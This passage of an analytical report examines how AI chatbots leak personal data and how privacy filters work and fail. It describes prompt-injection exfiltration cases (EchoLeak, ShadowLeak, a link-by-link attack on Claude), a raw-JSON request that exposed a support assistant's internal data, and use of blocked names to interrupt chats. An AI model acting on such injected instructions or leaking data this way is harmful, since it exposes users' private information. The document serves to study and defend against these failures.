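The lack of a reported bypass is weak evidence that a repair works, since few people may have tried to find one. The known failures are more informative, and they show several problems with lists of allowed domains. Allowed Teams and Bing domains fetched other addresses on request. Superhuman allowed `docs.google.com`, where Google Forms stores whatever data arrives in an address. Salesforce's policy still listed a domain whose registration had expired, so researchers from Noma Security registered it and received the data. Trusting a whole domain is risky when it hosts many services or can change hands. The travel agency would be safer listing the exact address of its logo.

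Limiting a tool to exact addresses from certain sources can still let personal data leak. Claude's tool for reading web pages could open only addresses that came from the user, a search, or a page it had already read. In July 2026, Willison reported an attack by Ayush Paul that used links on pages the tool had read. Paul built a website with a link for each letter and had Claude spell out the user's name by choosing which links to open. The attack also revealed the user's home city and employer. Anthropic then stopped the tool from following links on pages it had read.

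Some attacks leak data through the provider's servers rather than the user's browser. In the ShadowLeak attack, a hidden instruction in an email made ChatGPT's Deep Research feature open an address containing data from the user's inbox. OpenAI's servers sent the request, so a sanitiser or content policy in the browser could not have blocked it.

The time a product stays open after a report also varies:

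| Product | Reported | Repaired | Time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat | 8 April 2023 | 15 June 2023 | 68 days |
| Azure AI Playground | 24 July 2023 | 13 September 2023 | 51 days |
| Google's Generative AI Studio | 30 August 2023 | By 19 October 2023 | At most 50 days |
| Microsoft 365 Copilot, EchoLeak | January 2025 | May 2025 | About four months |
| ChatGPT, shared chats | 18 October 2026 | 26 October 2026 | 8 days |

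These five cases are too few to show that vendors have become faster. The ChatGPT flaw gave access to whole accounts, which may explain why OpenAI hurried.

### How common the flaws and attacks are

Case reports can't be used to estimate how common unsafe markup is in AI products, because nobody knows how many products researchers examined without finding any. Researchers prefer well-known products and those whose makers pay rewards for reported flaws, and they rarely write about unsuccessful attempts. Vendors may also fix flaws they find themselves without announcing them.

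The number of known flaws depends heavily on who is looking for them. In August 2025, Rehberger published one report a day on flaws in AI tools, so the increase that month reflects Rehberger's effort more than any change in the tools. Willison's 45 posts are no better as a count of flaws, since they include articles, talks and new product features.

A report of "no known exploitation" is also limited evidence that no attack occurred, because a successful attack can leave few traces. The user may see only a broken image or no image at all, and the EchoLeak attack included instructions for Copilot to hide their source. The company's network may record only a request to Teams or Bing. Attackers can also limit an attack to a few targets. Push Security had trouble reproducing the LLMShare advertisements, probably because they appeared only in certain places or at certain times.

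Vendors are in a better position to look for past attacks because they can search any model outputs they have kept for images with long, encoded URLs on outside domains. Researchers would have to run one fixed set of tests on a random sample of products and publish all the results, including those for products that passed, to find out how common the flaws are.

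## Privacy filters in deployed products

Companies rarely disclose how their products' privacy filters work, so outsiders tend to notice a filter only when it misfires. In late November 2024, users discovered that ChatGPT stopped mid-response whenever it was about to write the name "David Mayer".

### Names that stopped ChatGPT

When users asked about David Mayer, ChatGPT showed an error message such as "I'm unable to produce a response" and ended the chat. 404 Media's *Not Just David Mayer ChatGPT Breaks When Asked About Two Law Professors* reported the same error for Jonathan Zittrain and Jonathan Turley, and users soon found more names that triggered it. Ars Technica's *Certain names make ChatGPT grind to a halt, and we know why* (2024) lists five names that remained blocked after OpenAI unblocked "David Mayer".

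| Blocked name | Who it probably refers to | Known history |
|---|---|---|
| Brian Hood | An Australian mayor | Threatened to sue after ChatGPT falsely said he had gone to prison for bribery |
| Jonathan Turley | A law professor at George Washington University | Complained in 2023 that ChatGPT had invented a sexual harassment claim against him |
| Jonathan Zittrain | A law professor at Harvard | Has often spoken about the "right to be forgotten" |
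| Guido Scorza | A board member of Italy's data protection authority | No known dispute |
| David Faber | Unclear | No known dispute |

The block on Hood's name is probably the oldest. OpenAI settled its dispute with him in April 2023 by agreeing to filter out the false statements. According to Techdirt's *The Curious Case Of ChatGPT's Banned Names*, a reader of the technology blog noticed about a month after Hood's threat that ChatGPT failed when his name came up. The block drew little attention for another year and a half.

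OpenAI told The Guardian that one of its tools had "mistakenly flagged" David Mayer's name, and ZME Science reported that the name worked again less than a day later. In another statement, quoted by Mind Matters, OpenAI said ChatGPT may withhold some information about people to protect their privacy. It didn't answer Ars Technica's questions about the other names. According to The Independent's *ChatGPT is refusing to say five things*, users guessed that someone had filed a request under European data protection law, but nobody produced evidence of one. Legal action alone doesn't explain which names caused errors. Turley's name did, though he had not sued, and the name of Mark Walters, who had sued OpenAI for defamation, did not.

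The names that caused errors in ChatGPT caused none in OpenAI's API, the interface through which other companies' software uses its models. Ars Technica concluded that a fixed filter in ChatGPT stopped the output before it reached the user. Outsiders can rarely distinguish a filter's effects from the model's own behaviour this clearly.

Blocking an exact name affects everyone who shares it. If 1,000 people have the same name and users mention them equally often, 999 of every 1,000 blocked answers concern someone the block was not meant for. A teacher with a pupil called David Mayer could not have used ChatGPT to sort a class list. If a customer at the travel agency had that name, the employee would not have received the refund details either, because the filter stopped the whole answer instead of masking only the name.

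The block also gave outsiders a way to interrupt other people's chats. Riley Goodside of the data company Scale AI added "David Mayer" in faint type to a picture of an equation, and ChatGPT stopped when a user asked about the picture. A website could keep ChatGPT from summarising its pages by including a blocked name in the text.

A name filter also doesn't address Hood's complaint, which was about a false statement. An answer could repeat the falsehood without his name by calling him "the mayor who went to prison for bribery". A misspelt name would probably get through the filter too.

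### Instructions to the model are not a filter

Some developers try to protect data by using the system prompt, the instructions a model receives before each conversation, to tell it what not to reveal. In *I'll Have a Raw JSON, Please* (El Yadini, 2026), the security company Quarkslab describes testing a customer's support assistant that had such instructions. The assistant refused 129 attempts to make it talk about itself. But when the testers instead asked for raw JSON, a format programs use to exchange data, it returned its tool calls, retrieved documents and the output of its safety classifier.

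The instructions influenced how the model answered, but no program checked the answer. At the travel agency, a request for the raw booking record could return Lindqvist's passport number in the same way, even if the system prompt said never to mention passports. An output filter would at least scan the record, but it would have to handle structured data as well as sentences. El Yadini reproduced the attack in a simplified lab setup with an older model, GPT-4.1 mini, which shows how the attack works but not how often it succeeds.

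### PLLuM's output correction layer

PLLuM is a family of Polish language models that six research institutions built with government funding, partly for use in public administration. In *PLLuM*, Kocoń, Piasecki and colleagues (2025) describe the models' filter, Guard, in unusual detail. Guard is a separate program between the user and the model, so every question and answer passes through it.

Guard first uses a detector based on Presidio to look for names, addresses, phone numbers, email addresses and national ID numbers, and replaces them with placeholders such as "[PERSON]". Whoever installs Guard decides how much it masks. It then uses word lists, patterns and trained classifiers to check the text for other banned content.

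Guard can correct an answer only if it holds the complete text before displaying it. It can then have the model rewrite the offending part, check the new version and show it to the user, so a public office that wants corrected answers has to make people wait for them. If the answer appears sentence by sentence, the user may already have read the earlier sentences, so Guard ends the answer at the first violation and shows a refusal message.

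The published scores cover harmful content, and the classifier for it has a precision of 0.913 and a recall of 0.936. For verbal aggression, the precision is 0.640 and the recall is 0.680, which would give an F1 of about 0.66 rather than the published 0.760. The researchers also tested the complete system on 1,600 requests chosen by an ethics board, 1,000 of which it was supposed to refuse. Accuracy was 0.94 on both neutral and adversarial prompts.

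Kocoń and colleagues state that the masking step guarantees compliance with European data protection law and the EU's AI Act, but they report no recall or precision for personal data, so the claim has little support. OpenAI's researchers, who did publish scores for Privacy Filter, explicitly ruled out such a guarantee. Filtering is also harder in Polish than in English because names change with grammatical case. Marta, for example, becomes "Marty" or "Marcie", so a filter that searches for names it has already found has to recognise these forms too.

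### OneShield at IBM

Asthana, Zhang and colleagues (2025) built OneShield Privacy Guard at IBM. Their paper, *Deploying Privacy Guardrails for LLMs*, gives scores for personal data and describes two uses of the tool. On an internal IBM platform with about 30 language models, OneShield checks both prompts and answers. On GitHub, it scans text that volunteers submit to an open-source project for training language models, so it does not filter a model's output there.

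OneShield uses rules and trained classifiers to find possible personal data. A second component scores how sensitive each item is in its context. For example, a name next to a bank account number scores higher than a name alone. A policy for the relevant jurisdiction then determines whether to mask the item, block the text or let it through.

The table gives F1 scores for OneShield in both settings and for two other detectors. StarPII is a model for finding personal data in program code.

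| Type | OneShield, IBM platform | OneShield, GitHub | Presidio | StarPII |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Person | 0.98 | 0.95 | 0.91 | 0.87 |
| Date | 0.96 | 0.88 | 0.72 | 0.85 |
| Email address | 0.94 | 0.89 | 0.85 | 0.73 |
| Phone number | 0.89 | 0.82 | 0.77 | 0.71 |
| Location | 0.91 | 0.84 | 0.81 | 0.74 |
| National ID | 0.92 | 0.78 | – | – |
| Card number | 0.95 | – | 0.72 | 0.68 |

OneShield's scores fell by between 3 and 14 points for every type measured in both settings, so a product needs retesting when it is used on different texts. The comparison with the other detectors is weaker evidence because Asthana and colleagues don't give the size of the labelled test set or say which of the two settings supplied the texts for Presidio and StarPII. Presidio's 0.91 for people is also far above its 0.264 on PIIBench, which suggests much easier texts or more lenient scoring. The researchers report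 a detection rate above 95% across 26 languages but no scores for individual languages.

They also report that detection took about half a millisecond for prompts of up to 150 tokens. That would be extremely fast for a system with trained classifiers, and they don't name the hardware.

In three months on GitHub, OneShield flagged 8.25% of 1,256 submissions, or about 104. Asthana and colleagues estimate that this saved more than 300 hours of manual review, assuming 15 minutes per submission, or 314 hours for all 1,256. But people still reviewed the flagged submissions, and if that also took 15 minutes each, the saving falls to about 288 hours. The estimate also assumes that someone would otherwise have read every submission for privacy problems. The researchers don't report a manual check of the roughly 1,150 unflagged submissions, so the number of missed identifiers is unknown.

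Reviewers improved the OneShield filter. Early versions flagged historical figures and fictional characters, so the researchers connected it to public databases of well-known people. The finished system does not flag Barack Obama's name and date of birth. A private person who shares a celebrity's name might therefore lose protection, which would be the reverse of ChatGPT's problem.

### What cloud providers offer

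A company can buy a filter from its cloud provider instead of building one, but the products cover different data. In 2025, AWS's documentation for Amazon Bedrock listed about 30 built-in types of personal data, including names, ages, addresses, phone numbers, and national identifiers for the United States, Canada and Britain. Customers could block or mask each type and add their own regular expressions. The built-in passport type was for US passports, so the travel agency would have needed its own pattern for a Swedish customer like Lindqvist.

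Google Cloud's Model Armor was much narrower in its basic setting. It looked for card numbers, financial account numbers, two kinds of US government ID numbers and two kinds of Google Cloud credentials, so it would have let names and phone numbers through. An advanced setting could use the far larger set of detectors in Google's Sensitive Data Protection service. Microsoft's Azure offered a detector that covered dozens of languages and returned a confidence score with each finding, so customers could choose a threshold.

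These lists show what a filter looks for, but not how much of it the filter finds. A filter may also support a language without working well in it. Cisco's detector accepted Hindi text but missed far more personal data in it than in European languages.

### Real phone numbers in answers

For most consumer chatbots, the only evidence of how well they protect contact details comes from outside observation. In *ChatGPT Gave Out My Address and Phone Number*, Novak (2026) asked five of them for the journalist's own phone number.

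| Chatbot | Result |
|---|---|
| ChatGPT | Gave a former number and a former home address |
| Grok | Refused the number, even when told that it was a matter of life and death |
| Claude | Refused the number, citing privacy |
| Perplexity | Refused the number but gave a username for the messaging app Signal |
| Gemini | Refused the number but gave two public email addresses |

ChatGPT apparently found the old number and address in a PDF of a records request that Novak sent to a US government agency in 2016. Both were real and public, so to block them, a filter would have needed a rule against giving out private contact details even when they are online.

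Gemini named the owner of a phone number when Novak reversed the question and supplied the number, which Novak shares freely. The other four would not do this. A filter that masks phone numbers would miss this kind of disclosure because the number is in the question and the answer contains only a journalist's name. The filter would have to check the question and answer together.

Filters are also hard to identify from outside. Perplexity displayed Novak's email address as "[email protected]". It may have masked the address itself, or it may have copied the phrase from a web page, since the web security company Cloudflare uses exactly that phrase to hide addresses from automated programs. The refusals could likewise come from the model's training, its instructions or a separate filter. One person's questions also can't establish which chatbot is safest.

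Gemini Flash gave out the phone number of Fernando, a Spanish engineer, as a business contact. Novak mentions a software developer in Israel who started to receive customer service calls for the same reason. These errors also expose the private information of people who contact the wrong number. Pérez Colomé reports that one woman, who thought she was writing to a clinic, sent Fernando her name, her photograph and a question about a gynaecological treatment.

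The origin of Fernando's number is uncertain. According to Radar Digital's *Gemini and ChatGPT disclose engineer's personal phone number* (2026), he has had it since 2021 and suspects it once belonged to a company. Linda Petrini, an AI safety researcher, thinks it may have appeared on business websites and entered the models' data from there. José Hernández-Orallo, an AI researcher in Valencia and Cambridge, suggests the models may have generated it without a source, because they don't produce digits at random and can repeat the same combinations. Google also called it a possible hallucination, and a web search for the number found nothing. None of these accounts mentions a change to Gemini or ChatGPT in response.

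People outside the companies also cannot tell how often this happens. Fernando received at least eight calls and messages, but if only one in ten people who saw his number used it, about 80 people would have seen it. Google and OpenAI could search the answers they have kept for his number and check whether a filter had examined those answers. Press reports also favour failures that people notice, such as a wrong number that leads to a phone call or a blocked name that causes an error message. When a filter correctly masks an address, reporters have nothing to cover.

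A systematic study would need to ask chatbots the same questions about many people who had consented. In *AI Chatbots Are Giving Out People's Real Phone Numbers* (2026), the University of Washington Security and Privacy Research Lab announced that it was studying how people can use chatbots to find personal information, but gave no results.

### Whether hiding data counts as erasing it

According to Petrini, Fernando can ask Google and OpenAI to remove his number under the EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR). Its Article 17 entitles people to have their personal data erased in certain circumstances, such as when a company has processed it unlawfully. Unlike a database, a model has no row for each person that a company can easily delete, and retraining it without one person's data is expensive. Filtering the data out of answers is much cheaper. Whether this satisfies the law depends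 largely on whether the model itself contains personal data.

Hamburg's data protection authority argued in a 2024 discussion paper, *Large Language Models and Personal Data*, that a language model does not store personal data. In its view, the model stores mathematical relationships between fragments of words, so a right to erasure can't apply to it. People can still assert their rights over the system's inputs and outputs. On this reading, suppressing the output can fully satisfy an erasure request.

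The European Data Protection Board, which brings together the EU's national data protection authorities, said in *Opinion 28/2024* that a model trained on personal data isn't automatically anonymous. To treat a model as anonymous, a company has to show that the chance of someone extracting that data, or obtaining it through ordinary questions, is insignificant. If the company can't, the data may still be in the model, and a filter only makes it harder to reach. The Board nevertheless listed output filters among the measures that can reduce the risk to people.

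France's data protection authority, the CNIL, said in its 2025 recommendations that a company may use other effective measures, such as output filters, where retraining would be disproportionate. The CNIL prefers general rules against producing personal data to a list of people who have complained. ChatGPT's name blocks, which look like such a list, show the drawbacks of that approach.

The privacy organisation noyb rejects suppression as a substitute for correction or erasure. Its 2024 complaint to the Austrian authority concerned a public figure whose date of birth ChatGPT kept getting wrong. According to noyb, OpenAI said it couldn't correct the date and could block it only by blocking everything about the person. In 2025, noyb filed a complaint in Norway after ChatGPT falsely said a man had murdered his own children. ChatGPT had since begun to search the web and no longer repeated the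 story, but noyb argued that the false data might still be in the model and that hiding it from users wasn't enough.

A 2014 ruling by the EU's highest court is a precedent for treating suppression as sufficient. The court held that Google could have to remove links from the results of a search for a person's name, even though the linked pages stayed online. But the GDPR distinguishes the right to erasure from the right to restrict processing, under which a company keeps data and limits its use. A filter that leaves the model unchanged resembles restriction at least as much as erasure.

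OpenAI's name blocks covered one product but not the model behind it, so developers could still get the blocked names through the API. Anyone who downloads an open model can leave out the filter. Even under Hamburg's reading, a company would have to apply the filter everywhere it offers the model.

If Hernández-Orallo is right about Fernando's number, the model has no record of him to erase, and retraining it without his data might change nothing. A filter is then the more direct remedy. Blocking an exact phone number also does far less damage than blocking a name, because only one subscriber has the number at a time. The filter would have to mask the number instead of ending the answer, and stop masking it once it is reassigned.
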